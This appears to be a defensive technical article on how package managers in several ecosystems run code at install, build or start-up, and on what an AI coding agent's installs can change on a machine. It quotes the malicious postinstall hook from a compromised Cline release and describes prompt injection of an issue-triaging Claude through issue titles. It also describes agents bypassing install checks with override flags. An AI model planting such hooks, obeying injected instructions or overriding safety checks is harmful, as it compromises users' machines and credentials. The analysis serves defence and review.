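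The main drawback of allowing only wheels is that some installs fail. A package may have no wheel for the user's platform, or none yet for a new Python version. Users of alternative Python interpreters such as PyPy would be affected most, which is why a participant in *Preventing unwanted attempts to build sdists* objected to making wheels-only the default. pip may also install an older release that has a wheel, which is a problem if the project needs the newer one. An agent can often get past an error by rerunning the command without the wheels-only option, so if the option matters, the user should enforce it outside the agent's control.

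pypackaging-native, a website about the difficulties of packaging compiled code, reports that pip's maintainers agreed in principle to use only wheels by default. The issue has been open for years. A contributor to *Provide a way to signal an sdist isn't meant to be built?* wrote that the change needs funding and outreach, and that "perhaps it will never happen". In pip 26.2, wheels-only was still an option that users had to turn on.

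Developers have proposed several smaller steps:

- Projects that are hard to build could add `.manualbuild` to the names of their source distributions, so that installers would ignore them unless the user asked for a build.
- pip could refuse to build any project that publishes wheels for other platforms, again unless the user asked.
- *A proposal for sdist build complexity signaling, providing user agency* would let users choose a strategy for each package, such as never building it or building it only when no wheel fits.

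Most of this discussion is about sparing people failed builds of packages such as NumPy. The `.manualbuild` suffix wouldn't stop a malicious package, because its author would leave it off. Refusing to build projects that have wheels wouldn't help much either, because an attacker can publish a source distribution without a wheel. A wheels-only default would block both workarounds, but it is the hardest of these changes to make.

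### Start-up files

An attacker who publishes a wheel can still get code to run even if no one imports the package. The usual method is a `.pth` file in `site-packages`. Python reads these files whenever it starts. Most lines name a directory to search for modules, but Python executes any line that begins with `import`, according to its *site* documentation. Python allows several statements on one line, separated by semicolons, so that line can contain a whole program.

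In March 2026, an attacker added a file called `litellm_init.pth` to version 1.82.8 of litellm, a library for calling language models. The file sent cloud credentials and other secrets to the attacker's server. According to the Python Developer Tooling Handbook, it ran with any Python command, even `python -c "print(1)"`. About six weeks later, malicious releases of the machine-learning package lightning used ordinary import code instead, which started a background thread only when somebody imported the package.

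Agents start Python all the time to run tests, short scripts and pip. Because pip is a Python program, even running `pip uninstall litellm` from the affected environment would first have run the malicious file.

Start-up files also have ordinary uses. Editable installs, which let a developer change a package's source without reinstalling it, rely on `.pth` files to find that source. The tool coverage.py records which lines of a program its tests execute. A participant in *PEP 829*, a forum thread on changing the format, explains that coverage.py uses a `.pth` file to start measuring before a new Python process does anything else, and suggests that an environment variable could do this instead.

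Python also tries to import two modules at startup, `sitecustomize` and `usercustomize`. The first lets an administrator adjust Python for a whole installation, and the second does the same for one user. A package can install a file with either name.

A `.pth` file in a virtual environment disappears when someone deletes that environment. Python also reads `.pth` files in the user's own package directory, which on Linux is normally under `~/.local/lib`. A file that a build script writes there outlasts the project and affects other Python programs that the user runs outside virtual environments. pip's record of installed files doesn't include it.

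For inspection, `python -S` turns off all start-up files. The `-I` option ignores the user's package directory and Python's environment variables, but still reads the environment's own start-up files.

### PEP 829 and the new `.start` files

*PEP 829* (Warsaw, 2026) proposed separating the two jobs of a `.pth` file. Python's Steering Council, the elected committee that decides on changes to the language, accepted it on April 24, 2026, according to *What is PEP 829?* in the Python Developer Tooling Handbook. Python 3.15, released on October 9, is the first version to include the change.

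`.pth` files keep the job of adding directories. Code moves to `.start` files, which contain lines such as:

```text
foo.submod:initialize
```

When Python starts, it imports the module `foo.submod` and calls its `initialize` function. The function can do anything, but its code has to be in an importable module rather than on a line of a configuration file. Python adds all the directories from `.pth` files to its module search path before it calls the functions in `.start` files, so those functions can use modules from any of the directories.

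Python is phasing out the old `import` lines slowly:

| Python version | What happens to `import` lines in `.pth` files |
|---|---|
| 3.14 and earlier | Python runs them |
| 3.15 to 3.17 | Python runs them, unless there is a `.start` file with the same base name |
| 3.18 and 3.19 | Python silently ignores them |
| 3.20 | Python ignores them and prints a warning |

If Python keeps to one release a year, version 3.18 will arrive in late 2029. Warsaw explained in *PEP 829* that the two years without warnings are needed because packages that support both old and new versions of Python will have to include both files for a while, and users would otherwise see warnings they could do nothing about.

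In its acceptance, posted in *PEP 829*, the Steering Council asked Warsaw to state that the overall threat of a malicious package running code at startup is "unchanged". The Council said the benefit is that people can inspect which function a package will call, instead of having to interpret a string of code.

This is more accurate than the Handbook's claim that the change closes off the method used against litellm. The exact file used in that attack will stop working on Python 3.18, but the attacker could move the code into a module and add a one-line `.start` file, which is no harder than what the jscrambler attacker did within a few hours.

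The new format does make start-up code easier to find. A tool can look for files ending in `.start` instead of parsing every `.pth` file for all the ways to write an `import` line. One participant in the debate objected that this improves auditing, not security. That's fair, although auditing can improve security if somebody does it. On an agent's machine, a list of new files would be enough to show that a package had added start-up code.

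### Where should the check go?

In the thread *Idea*, packaging developers also discussed a proposal for installers to block start-up files, or at least warn about them, unless the user or the installer's developers had approved the package. The proposer argued that existing packages rarely have a good reason to suddenly add such a file. Another participant found only two `.pth` files in an environment full of assorted packages, from setuptools and coverage.py, so a short list of approved packages might be practical.

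Others expected people to ignore the warnings. A user who sees that a tool includes a `.pth` file has no easy way to tell whether it should. Prompts also interrupt automated installs, and one participant admitted to always using another package manager's `-y` option, which approves everything in advance.

The alternative these critics supported most was to act on PyPI. Its administrators could quarantine a release that suddenly added a `.pth` file and approve the few legitimate cases in advance. This would leave the decision to people who understand the files and protect users of every installer, but not anyone who installs from another index. Warsaw similarly argued for changing Python itself because not everyone uses pip or PyPI.

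Several developers doubted that start-up files deserved this much attention. A malicious package has other options:

- It can overwrite a file that belongs to a popular package, because installers let the most recently installed file win.
- It can publish only a source distribution, with a malicious backend.
- It can install a command called `pathlib.py` next to pip's own command. The next time the user runs pip, Python may load that file instead of its standard `pathlib` module.
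- It can hide harmful behavior in compiled code and trigger it only occasionally, so that tests are unlikely to catch it.

The reply was that some of these are even more suspicious than a `.pth` file and just as easy to detect, so installers or PyPI should check for all of them. This seems right for overwritten files and odd command names, but it doesn't help with compiled code, where the file list may show nothing unusual. One participant wondered whether the standard advice might soon be to build audited source distributions yourself, which would reverse the move towards wheels.

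*PEP 829* also includes an argument for doing nothing, on the grounds that the benefits don't justify the disruption. That argument is somewhat persuasive if the only goal is to stop attackers. It is less so for someone trying to find out what an install changed, because they are less likely to miss start-up files that are easier to spot.

Another suggestion in *Idea* was a `pip audit` command that would run after each install and look for start-up code, altered files and files in unexpected places. A participant pointed out that pip is usually installed in the environment it would be checking, so a malicious package could tamper with the check. The tool would have to run from a separate Python environment or finish before any of the new code runs.

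## Install-time code in Rust, Ruby, PHP and system package managers

pip runs build code during the install command. Rust's package manager usually runs it later, when someone builds the project, and Debian's runs package scripts as root. To work out what an agent's install did, you need to know when the package's code runs, with what privileges, whether the user can switch it off, and whether the package can clean up when someone removes it.

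*The Hitchhiker's Guide to Malicious Third-Party Dependencies* (Ladisa, Sahin and colleagues, 2023) compares seven package managers. It reports ways to run code at install time in npm, pip, Composer, RubyGems and Cargo, but none in Go or Maven (Java). The comparison is still a good starting point, but it is wrong about Composer, and RubyGems has changed since.

### Rust: code that runs at the first build

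Cargo is Rust's package manager. Running `cargo add serde` adds a line to the project's manifest, `Cargo.toml`, and runs none of the package's code. That code can first run when someone builds the project.

If a package has a `build.rs` file, Cargo compiles it and runs it just before building the package, according to Rust's *Build Scripts*. This applies to dependencies too. Build scripts typically compile a C library, look for one on the system, or generate Rust code. Commands such as `cargo test` and `cargo check` also run them, and `cargo install` downloads, builds and installs a program in one step.

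According to Rust's documentation, a build script should write only to the directory named in the `OUT_DIR` variable, but Cargo doesn't enforce this. The script runs with the permissions of whoever started the build. Cargo hides the script's output, as npm does with hooks, but saves a copy under the project's `target` directory. That copy can reveal a download if the script honestly reported it.

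As with pip's cached wheels, repeating an agent's build may not run any build scripts, because Cargo reruns a build script only when it detects a relevant change. Deleting the `target` directory first makes Cargo run them again.

Cargo has no general setting to turn off build scripts. If a package's manifest declares that it links to a particular C library, the user can supply the library's details in a settings file, and Cargo then skips the script. This works for one library at a time, and a malicious author can leave out the declaration.

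Packages can also contain procedural macros, which are functions that generate Rust code. The compiler loads and runs them while it compiles any package that uses them. They have the same access to files and the network as the compiler. Ladisa and colleagues recommend checking dependencies for build scripts, but that check misses macros. A package that defines macros of this kind must set `proc-macro = true` in its `Cargo.toml`, which makes them easy to search for.

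Opening a Rust project in an editor can run build scripts without anyone typing a build command. JetBrains' *Evaluating Build Scripts in the IntelliJ Rust Plugin* (2022) explains that an editor needs the code these scripts generate to offer completions, and that the plug-in began running them by default. rust-analyzer, which provides Rust support in many other editors, also runs them by default. A developer who opens a project to review an agent's new dependency may therefore be the first to run the dependency's code.

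### Ruby: extensions and plug-ins

RubyGems installs Ruby packages, which are called gems. Many gems wrap a C library and need compiling, including the XML library nokogiri and the database clients pg and mysql2. According to RubyGems' guide to extensions, such a gem usually includes an `extconf.rb` file that prepares the build. RubyGems runs this file, an ordinary Ruby program, during `gem install`.

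Extensions can also be written in Rust, in which case `gem install` starts Cargo, which downloads Rust packages and runs their build scripts. One Ruby command can therefore run code from two registries, but Ruby's lockfile lists only the gems. The guide advises authors to include Cargo's lockfile in the gem so that everyone at least gets the same Rust dependencies.

A gem without an extension can still run code by including a plug-in for RubyGems itself. In Ruby's installer source, RubyGems loads the plug-in near the end of the install, after writing the gem's files. It loads the plug-in again on later `gem` commands, much as Python rereads its start-up files. Users can also write plug-ins to protect themselves. An example in RubyGems' plug-in guide asks before installing any gem that isn't on the user's list, and stops the install if the user says no.

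According to RubyGems' command reference, if a gem's extension doesn't compile, the unpacked gem stays on disk but RubyGems doesn't write the specification file that registers it as installed. If an agent tries three database gems and only the third works, the two failed gems may remain on disk without appearing in `gem list`.

Ladisa and colleagues found no option to skip extensions, and the reference for RubyGems 4.0 doesn't list one either. Ruby's commit log for April 2026 includes work on two switches, `--no-build-extension` and `--no-install-plugin`, and on support for them in Bundler, the tool that installs a Ruby project's dependencies. RubyGems 4.1, released on November 16, is probably the first version to have them, and `gem install --help` shows whether a given machine does. *What's New in RubyGems/Bundler 4.1* (SHIBATA, 2026) lists `gem install --cooldown 7`, which skips versions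 less than a week old, among the security features.

### PHP: scripts and plug-ins

Composer, PHP's package manager, has a `scripts` field that looks like npm's. According to Composer's documentation, only scripts in the root package, the project in which someone runs Composer, are run. This contradicts Ladisa and colleagues, who describe the field as a way for a malicious dependency to run commands. Running Composer in a freshly cloned repository still carries the same risk as running npm there. Composer's `--no-scripts` option skips these scripts, although Ladisa and colleagues report that Composer can't skip them.

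Composer dependencies run code through plug-ins. A package becomes a plug-in by declaring the type `composer-plugin` and naming a PHP class, which Composer loads and runs. Plug-ins put packages in unusual directories, configure framework modules and check licenses, among other things. Packagist's *Composer 2.2 Release* announced `allow-plugins`, a setting in the project's `composer.json` that lists which plug-ins may run and allows none by default.

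On April 30, 2026, an attacker turned version 5.0.2 of `intercom/intercom-php`, previously an ordinary library, into a Composer plug-in that collected cloud credentials and SSH keys. Composer asks before it enables a new plug-in, so the code should have run only if somebody answered yes, the project already allowed the plug-in, or Composer was too old to ask. Packagist's *Restricting Composer plugins across your organization* explains this prompt but also says that Composer ran the attacker's code in any project that updated, which seems too strong. It argues more convincingly that people readily approve a package they already use, and that the prompt is even easier to miss when an AI coding agent is making the change.

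When no one is there to answer the prompt, Composer can stop with an error. In a build log on Drupal's issue tracker, the error for a blocked plug-in includes the command that would enable it. Running that command is the obvious next step for an agent trying to fix the build. The approval then appears in the project's diff, but unlike npm's default approvals, it isn't tied to a version, and an entry such as `symfony/*` covers every plug-in from one vendor.

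Companies can take this choice away from agents with Packagist's paid service, which can leave unapproved plug-ins out of the package list it sends to Composer. When a plug-in is missing from the list, Composer's error suggests a typo in the package name, which might lead an agent to try other names. Composer can still install unapproved plug-ins from an existing lockfile unless an administrator also blocks the downloads.

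### A Debian package from installation to removal

On Debian and related systems such as Ubuntu, `apt` downloads packages and a lower-level program, `dpkg`, installs them. A package can include four maintainer scripts, called `preinst`, `postinst`, `prerm` and `postrm`. `dpkg` needs root privileges to write to system directories, and the scripts normally run with the same privileges.

Suppose an agent runs `sudo apt install exampled`, where `exampled` is an imaginary server program with its own user account. The sequence below follows Debian's *Package maintainer scripts and installation procedure*, with typical actions filled in:

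1. `preinst` runs before `dpkg` unpacks the package. It can't use the package's own files yet, so it usually only prepares the system, for example by moving an old data file.
2. `dpkg` unpacks the program, its documentation and its configuration files.
3. `postinst` runs with the files in place. It creates a system user called `exampled`, makes a data directory that this user owns, and enables and starts the service.
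4. When someone later removes the package, `prerm` runs first and stops the service.
5. `dpkg` deletes the package's files but keeps its configuration files.
6. `postrm` cleans up what is left. It runs again if the user purges the package, which also deletes the configuration files.

The new account and the running service are both hidden changes, though both are normal for a server package. The package's author may not have written the code that sets them up. Debhelper, a set of packaging tools, generates the usual commands for services, according to a related manual page reproduced with dpkg's *deb-prerm(5)* (2018).

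Scripts can ask questions during setup, but Debian requires them to work without a terminal, so an agent's install tends to get the default answers. Linuxtopia's *Debian maintenance scripts*, an old copy of Debian's reference guide, notes that some scripts warn users who accept the defaults to reconfigure the package later. An agent may see that warning only as one line in a long log.

How thoroughly removal cleans up depends on the package author's scripts. `postrm` may run after the package's dependencies are gone, and Debian tells authors to skip any cleanup that needs a missing one. `deluser`, the usual command for deleting an account, comes in a separate package, so `postrm` may be unable to delete an account the package created. Many authors also leave these accounts in place deliberately, because a new account could otherwise get the same numeric ID and take ownership of leftover files.

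A failed install can leave more behind. If `preinst` fails on a first install, `dpkg` calls `postrm` to undo its work. If `postinst` fails, `dpkg` marks the package as half-configured and doesn't undo anything, so the user account may already exist even though the install reported an error. Debian requires the scripts to be safe to run again, and `apt` will usually retry the configuration the next time it installs something.

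During an upgrade, `dpkg` temporarily backs up the files it replaces, but after a certain step it no longer restores the old version. The backups also don't cover whatever the scripts changed.

An install can run scripts from packages the agent didn't name. If the new package conflicts with an installed one, `dpkg` may remove the installed one and run its removal scripts.

`dpkg` runs a package's scripts as root and has no ordinary option for installing the package without them. Running `dpkg-deb --control` on a downloaded package extracts the scripts so they can be read before they run. After installation, they are in `/var/lib/dpkg/info`. Reading the scripts is more useful for a package from a vendor's website than for one from Debian's own archive, where Debian's developers maintain the packages.

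### Homebrew and conda

Homebrew, a package manager for macOS, describes each command-line package in a Ruby file called a formula. A formula can include a `post_install` step, which Homebrew runs even when it installs a prebuilt copy. Homebrew normally refuses to run as root. On macOS, it runs this step in a sandbox that limits where the step can write, a restriction that pip's build isolation lacks. The `--skip-post-install` option turns the step off.

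Homebrew formulas have no matching uninstall step. Casks, which install ready-made Mac applications, can list uninstall steps but can also run a vendor's installer with administrator privileges.

conda installs packages for Python and other languages into separate environments. A package can include a `post-link` script, which runs after conda puts its files in place, and a `pre-unlink` script, which runs before removal. They have the user's permissions and no sandbox. conda has no ordinary option to skip them, but pixi, a newer tool that installs the same packages, skips them by default.

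conda packages can also add scripts that run whenever someone activates the environment. These work like Python's start-up files, except that they run in the user's shell.

### Go, where fetching runs no hook

Ladisa and colleagues found that Go has no install hooks, so `go get` and `go mod download` fetch a module without running code from it. Go's developers also aim to keep builds from running a module's code, and Go has no equivalent of `build.rs`. Module authors who need generated code usually run the generator themselves and publish the result. `go generate` can run a module's generator commands, but only when someone invokes it.

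There are a few exceptions and near-exceptions:

- **C code.** Go can compile C files in a module, and the module can pass options to the C compiler. In 2018, Go's developers fixed a flaw that let a package run its own code by telling the compiler to load a plug-in. Go now restricts which options a module can pass.
- **Newer versions of Go.** Since Go 1.21, a module can require a newer version of Go than the one installed, and the `go` command may download and run that version. The program comes from the Go project, not the module's author, but it is still a change outside the project. Setting `GOTOOLCHAIN=local` prevents it.
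- **Running the program.** A module's `init()` functions run when a program that imports it starts, before the program's own main code. `go test` and `go run` both do this.

Go modules are also easier to check before use than Ruby gems. Go identifies modules by their source repositories, so Tournoij (2026), in *Dependencies should be fetched directly from VCS*, reviews updates by reading the commits between two versions. A gem's author uploads a separate archive, which may not match the repository. Few agents or people will read every commit, but with Go they can do so before any of the code runs.

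### The mechanisms compared

| Mechanism | When it runs | Privileges | Can the user switch it off? | Can the package supply a removal step? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cargo build script | Just before Cargo builds the package | User's | Only for packages that declare a linked library | No |
| Rust procedural macro | While the compiler builds code that uses it | User's | No | No |
| RubyGems extension | During `gem install` | User's | Yes, in versions with `--no-build-extension` | No |
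| RubyGems plug-in | During `gem install` and later `gem` commands | User's | Yes, in versions with `--no-install-plugin` | Yes, through uninstall hooks |
| Composer root script | During `composer install` or `update` | User's | Yes, with `--no-scripts` | Yes, but only the root project can |
| Composer plug-in | During Composer commands | User's | Off until approved | Yes, through an `uninstall` method |
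| Debian maintainer scripts | Before and after unpacking and removal | Usually root | No ordinary option | Yes, `prerm` and `postrm` |
| Homebrew `post_install` | After Homebrew installs the files | User's, in a sandbox on macOS | Yes, with `--skip-post-install` | No |
| conda link scripts | After linking and before unlinking | User's | No ordinary option in conda | Yes, `pre-unlink` |
| Go module | No hook on fetching or building | Not applicable | Not needed | No |

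"User's" means the permissions of whoever started the command, so `sudo gem install` gives an extension root privileges.

Package managers that clean up well are not necessarily safer. Debian packages have the most complete removal steps, but also the most power over the machine. Go packages have neither removal steps nor that power, and leave less to clean up.

### What "install" has to include

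An agent adding a Rust dependency might run `cargo add` and then `cargo test`. The package's build script doesn't run until `cargo test`, so a tool that monitors only commands containing "install" or "add" would miss it.

A record of an install should therefore start when the package is requested and end when the first build that uses it succeeds. It will include some unrelated changes, because the project's own build also writes files. It will miss package code that runs only once the program is running, but capturing that code would mean recording everything the software ever does.

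With Cargo, it helps to download dependencies and build them in separate steps. `cargo fetch` downloads the dependencies without running their code, and the build can then run in a container with no network access. A build script that tries to download something will fail there, and the agent or the user can check what it tried to download before deciding whether to allow it.

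## Changes outside the project: global installs, shell profiles and caches

An install can change the rest of the machine without running any of a package's own code. `npm install -g eslint` makes ESLint available to every project, and the standard installer for Rust edits the user's shell profile. These changes outlast the agent's session, and some determine which program runs when someone types a command such as `python3`.

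### How the shell chooses a program

When someone types `conda`, the shell looks for a function of that name or for a program file in the directories listed in the `PATH` variable, as conda's *Deep dive* explains. It searches those directories in order and runs the first match. In an example from a Mac in conda's documentation, conda's own directory comes first, Homebrew's `/opt/homebrew/bin` second, and the system's `/usr/bin` further down.

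On this machine, `python3` runs conda's Python. Running `brew install python` wouldn't change that, because Homebrew's directory comes second in `PATH`, after conda's. But `brew install git` would make `git` run Homebrew's copy instead of the one in `/usr/bin`, including in scripts that call `git` by name.

A script whose first line gives the full path to its interpreter, such as `/usr/bin/python3`, skips the search. Many of an operating system's own tools do this, so changes to the search path rarely break them.

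npm projects have a further complication. A local install links a package's programs into `./node_modules/.bin`, according to npm, which makes them available to scripts that npm runs. `npm run lint` can therefore run the project's copy of ESLint, a code checker, while `eslint .` in a terminal runs the global copy. An agent that tests with the first command and tells the user to run the second may be recommending a different version.

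In bash and zsh, `type -a eslint` lists every match in order. Comparing its output before and after an install shows whether a new program has displaced an old one.

### Where global installs write

These are the usual locations on Linux, except for Homebrew, where the paths are for a Mac with Apple's own processors:

| Command | Package files | Programs | Who gets them |
|---|---|---|---|
| `npm install -g` | `/usr/local/lib/node_modules` | `/usr/local/bin` | Everyone on the machine |
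| `npm install -g` under nvm | `~/.nvm/versions/node/<version>/lib/node_modules` | The same version's `bin` directory | One user, with one version of Node.js |
| `pip install --user` | `~/.local/lib` | `~/.local/bin` | One user |
| `pipx install` | `~/.local/share/pipx/venvs` | `~/.local/bin` | One user |
| `uv tool install` | `~/.local/share/uv/tools` | `~/.local/bin` | One user |
| `brew install` | `/opt/homebrew/Cellar` | `/opt/homebrew/bin` | Usually everyone |
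| `apt install` | Mostly `/usr`, with settings in `/etc` | `/usr/bin` | Everyone |

nvm lets a user switch between versions of Node.js. Each version has its own global packages, so a tool that an agent installs under Node 20 can seem to vanish when the user switches to Node 22. nvm's *Node Version Manager* documentation also warns of mismatches on shared machines, where other users still run the packages in `/usr/local`.

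pipx and uv's `tool` command install Python programs. Each program gets its own virtual environment, so its dependencies can't conflict with another program's, and only the commands themselves go into the shared `~/.local/bin`. Neither installer overwrites a command that the other put there unless the user adds `--force`, according to pipx's *Comparisons*. An agent that uses `--force` to get past this error replaces the copy the user already had. pipx has a safer option, `--suffix`, which keeps both copies under different names.

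### The "externally managed" marker

Linux distributions write some of their tools in Python and run them with the same `/usr/bin/python3` that users run. If someone uses pip outside a virtual environment, those tools can import the new packages too. *PEP 668* (Thomas, Klose and colleagues, 2021) gives the example of Fedora's package manager, `dnf`, which a `pip install` can break by accident. The damage is hard to repair because people would normally use `dnf` to do it.

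*PEP 668* lets a distribution mark its Python as externally managed, meaning that `apt`, `dnf` or a similar program manages its packages. The marker is a file named `EXTERNALLY-MANAGED` in Python's standard library directory, for example `/usr/lib/python3.9`. PyPA's *Externally Managed Environments* tells installers to check whether they are running outside a virtual environment and whether the file exists. If both are true, pip stops with an error. Debian announced its marker in a February 2023 notice, which git.coop's *Debian Bookworm PEP 668* reproduces. Homebrew's Python also has the marker.

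The error message explains how to override the check. The Homebrew version, which Inventive HQ quotes, recommends `brew install` or a virtual environment, then mentions that you can pass `--break-system-packages` "at the risk of breaking your Python installation or OS". An agent trying to finish a task may add the flag. The install will probably succeed, and any conflict will appear later, when somebody runs the affected system tool.

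Suppose a system tool on Debian works with version 1 of a library, and the agent runs `sudo pip install --break-system-packages` for a package that needs version 2. pip puts version 2 under `/usr/local`, and apt's copy of version 1 stays under `/usr`. Python looks in `/usr/local` first, so the tool now imports version 2 and may crash. apt's records still list version 1 as correctly installed.

Removing version 2 would fix that machine. Recovery is harder on a system that keeps both kinds of package in one directory, because pip may delete the distribution's version during the upgrade. Thomas and colleagues warn that `sudo pip uninstall` can then remove more of the system's packages. Their standard therefore also forbids installers to delete files outside the directories they are installing into. Debian had already patched its pip to prevent such deletions, but some users still reported them.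 Thomas and colleagues suspect that these users had run `sudo pip install --upgrade pip` and replaced the patched copy with an unpatched one.

The flag can cause trouble even without `sudo`. A participant in *PEP 668*, a forum thread on the standard, points out that pip installs into the user's own directory when it can't write to the system directory. According to Arch Linux's copy of the pip manual, the user's directory is typically `~/.local`. *Pip installs to unexpected place* (Wichmann, 2025) quotes Grant Edwards, another mailing-list participant, who argues that packages there can break things only for that user. Services running under other accounts are unaffected, but the system's Python searches `~/.local` when this user starts one of its tools, so this limit offers little protection on a laptop with one user.

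The override can also become permanent. Another message in the forum thread suggests setting `PIP_BREAK_SYSTEM_PACKAGES=1`. If an agent puts that line in a shell profile, later pip commands skip the check even without the flag.

The override is occasionally justified. Thomas and colleagues mention people who want the distribution's copy of Ansible, a tool for configuring servers, to load an extension from PyPI. In a container that runs a single application, a mistake is easy to undo because the user can rebuild the container. For most of what an agent does on someone's own computer, a virtual environment works just as well, and pipx or `uv tool` can install command-line programs.

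### Two projects that share one tool

Giving each tool its own environment doesn't help when two projects need different versions of the same tool. Suppose the test scripts in two Python projects run `ruff check` to find errors in the code. Neither project lists Ruff as a dependency, so both use the copy the user installed with `uv tool install ruff==0.5.0`.

1. An agent working on the first project finds a setting that requires Ruff 0.6 or later. It runs `uv tool upgrade ruff`, but Ruff stays at 0.5.0 because upgrades respect the version requested at installation, according to Astral's *Tools*.
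2. The agent runs `uv tool install ruff==0.6.2`, which replaces the old version. The first project's tests pass.
3. A week later, the user runs the tests for the second project, which contains Jupyter notebooks. Ruff began checking notebooks by default in version 0.6, so the tests now fail on files that nobody has edited.

Ruff isn't in either lockfile, so neither has changed, and Git shows no changes in the second project. The explanation is in the log of an agent session about a different project.

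`uvx ruff@0.5.0` would work for now, but a better fix is to add Ruff to each project as a development dependency and run it with `uv run ruff`. Each lockfile then records the version its project needs. Although `uvx` normally runs a tool without installing it, plain `uvx ruff` wouldn't solve the problem because it uses the installed version by default, according to Astral's documentation.

### Lines in shell profiles

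rustup, the standard installer for Rust, edits the user's shell profile by default. Its output, which the laser-simulation library lasy reproduces in its installation guide, names `~/.profile` and `~/.zshenv` among the files it changes. The new line loads a small script that puts `~/.cargo/bin` at the front of the search path. A comment in the script, quoted in the forum thread *Rustup set an insecure PATH*, explains that the user may need to override a Rust compiler that came with the system.

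`cargo install` puts programs in the same directory as Rust's own tools, according to Rust's documentation, so a program that shares a name with a system command will run in its place. The forum thread's original poster worried that an attacker could add a fake `sudo` to collect passwords. Someone replied that an attacker with access to the account could change the search path anyway. That seems right for malicious hooks, which already have this access, but names could still clash by accident.

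nvm's install script downloads nvm to `~/.nvm` and adds lines to a profile such as `~/.bashrc` or `~/.zshrc`. Setting `PROFILE=/dev/null` for the script prevents the edit.

`conda init` writes a marked block of code into the shell profile, and on Windows it can change the registry instead. New terminals then usually start in conda's base environment, where `python` runs conda's Python. With `--system`, the change applies to every user. conda makes the edit easier to inspect than most installers do. `--dry-run` lists the files it would change, and `--verbose` shows the exact changes. `--reverse` undoes the last `conda init`. Deleting conda's directory doesn't remove the block, so the course notes for *Advanced Informatics, Winter 2021* tell students to delete it separately.

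An agent may not see the effect of its own edit to a shell profile. Bash doesn't read the usual profile files when it runs non-interactively, according to nvm's instructions for containers, and programs often run single commands this way. After installing nvm, an agent could get a "command not found" error and add the same lines to a second file. The user's next terminal may then load both files.

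### Caches

Caches are usually the largest of these changes and the least important. npm keeps downloads in `~/.npm`, and uv uses `~/.cache/uv` on Linux, according to Astral's *Storage*. Playwright, a browser-testing tool, puts its browsers in `~/.cache/ms-playwright`, where each can take up hundreds of megabytes. ccache, which saves compiled C and C++ code for reuse, normally uses `~/.cache/ccache`. Deleting these directories may slow the next install, test or build while the tools download or compile the files again.

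A cache can still affect which code runs. `uvx` reuses the version it has cached, so two people who run the same command on the same day can get different versions. uv also has an experimental feature that keeps projects' virtual environments in the cache. `uv cache clean` deletes them, and uv recreates them the next time they're needed.

uv's other directory, `~/.local/share/uv`, is easy to mistake for a cache. It contains installed tools and copies of Python, and deleting it to save space breaks programs that depend on them.

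### Package-manager and Git settings

One line in a settings file can affect every project. npm reads `~/.npmrc`, pip reads `~/.config/pip/pip.conf` on Linux, and uv reads user settings from `~/.config/uv` and system-wide settings from `/etc/uv`.

`npm install -g` may fail because the user can't write to `/usr/local`. A common fix is to choose another location with `npm config set prefix ~/.npm-global`, which adds a line to `~/.npmrc`. But according to nvm's documentation, a `prefix` setting in this file is incompatible with nvm. An agent that uses this fix to install one tool can therefore interfere with how the user switches between Node.js versions. Changing the `registry` setting in the same file would have a wider effect, because npm would then fetch packages from the new address in every project without its own `registry` setting. `~/.npmrc` can also contain saved approvals for install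 hooks.

Git keeps a user's settings in `~/.gitconfig`. Git LFS, an extension for storing large files, adds filters there when someone runs `git lfs install`. Those filters are usually wanted, but other changes made for one project can cause problems in others. For example, to install a private dependency, an agent might tell Git to replace SSH addresses with HTTPS ones. If it uses `--global`, the rule also applies to the user's other repositories, where only SSH may be set up. `git config --list --show-origin` lists each setting with the file it comes from.

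### Background services and agent configuration

A background service can keep running after the agent's session ends and start again when the user logs in. On Linux, the files that define a user's own services are usually in `~/.config/systemd/user`, and on macOS they are in `~/Library/LaunchAgents`. OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent that runs on the user's computer, can set up such a service. *Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected* (Likhith, 2026) describes the service as a gateway that accepts local connections on port 18789 and can run shell commands.

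Coding agents have user-level configuration too. OpenSkillIndex's *Install and Update nvm* includes a command that copies a skill, a folder of instructions for an agent, into `~/.claude/skills`. Claude Code can then use those instructions in any project, even after the user has forgotten about them.

Some configuration files can start programs. SafeDep's *Config Files That Run Code* describes a worm called Miasma that added such files to repositories. In one project, a commit labeled as a dependency update added five small files that launched a sixth, which stole credentials. Each of the five was triggered by a routine action, such as opening the folder, starting an agent session, installing dependencies or running tests. Most of the editors and agents first asked the user to trust the folder, but SafeDep says people click through these prompts without reading them.

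Reviewers could at least have found Miasma's files in the project's diff. Claude Code also reads session-start commands from `~/.claude/settings.json`, which applies to all of a user's projects and normally appears in none of their diffs. An install hook can write to that file.

For someone checking a machine after an agent's session, the caches can usually wait:

| Change | Where to look | Effect after the session |
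|---|---|---|
| Global program | `/usr/local/bin`, `~/.local/bin` | Can change the version that other projects run |
| Package in the system's Python | `/usr/local/lib`, `~/.local/lib` | Can break system tools |
| Shell profile | `~/.bashrc`, `~/.zshrc`, `~/.profile` | Affects new terminals |
| Package-manager and Git settings | `~/.npmrc`, `~/.gitconfig` | Affect later commands in other projects |
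| Background service | `~/.config/systemd/user`, `~/Library/LaunchAgents` | May keep running and restart at login |
| Agent configuration | `~/.claude` | Affects later agent sessions |
| Cache | `~/.npm`, `~/.cache` | Mostly disk use |

### The Cline release that installed OpenClaw

On February 17, 2026, a release of Cline CLI, an open-source coding agent, installed OpenClaw on users' computers without telling them. An attacker had used a stolen token to publish Cline 2.3.0 on npm at 3:26 a.m. Pacific time. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* compares it with version 2.2.3. Apart from the version number, the only meaningful change was a new hook in `package.json`:

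```json
"postinstall": "npm install -g openclaw@latest"
```

Cline had tried to revoke the stolen token a week earlier. In December 2025, it had set up Claude to sort incoming GitHub issues, with permission to run shell commands. Adnan Khan, a security researcher, found that anyone could put instructions to Claude in an issue's title as a first step towards stealing Cline's publishing credentials. Khan reported the flaw on January 1, but Cline didn't act until he made it public on February 9. Cline's *Postmortem* (2026) says that staff removed the vulnerable setup within 30 minutes, then deleted the wrong npm token. They checked a page that showed no active tokens, but it didn't list the exposed one. The Hacker News (2026) presents Khan's method as the one the attacker used, while SafeDep says nobody has publicly confirmed how the token was stolen.

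StepSecurity, the company that published Likhith's analysis, flagged the release after 14 minutes. The release had a new hook and hadn't come from Cline's usual automated release process. According to OSV's *Unauthorized npm publish of cline@2.3.0 with modified postinstall script* (2026), Cline published a clean version, 2.4.0, at 11:23 a.m. and marked 2.3.0 as deprecated seven minutes later. The altered release had been available for about eight hours.

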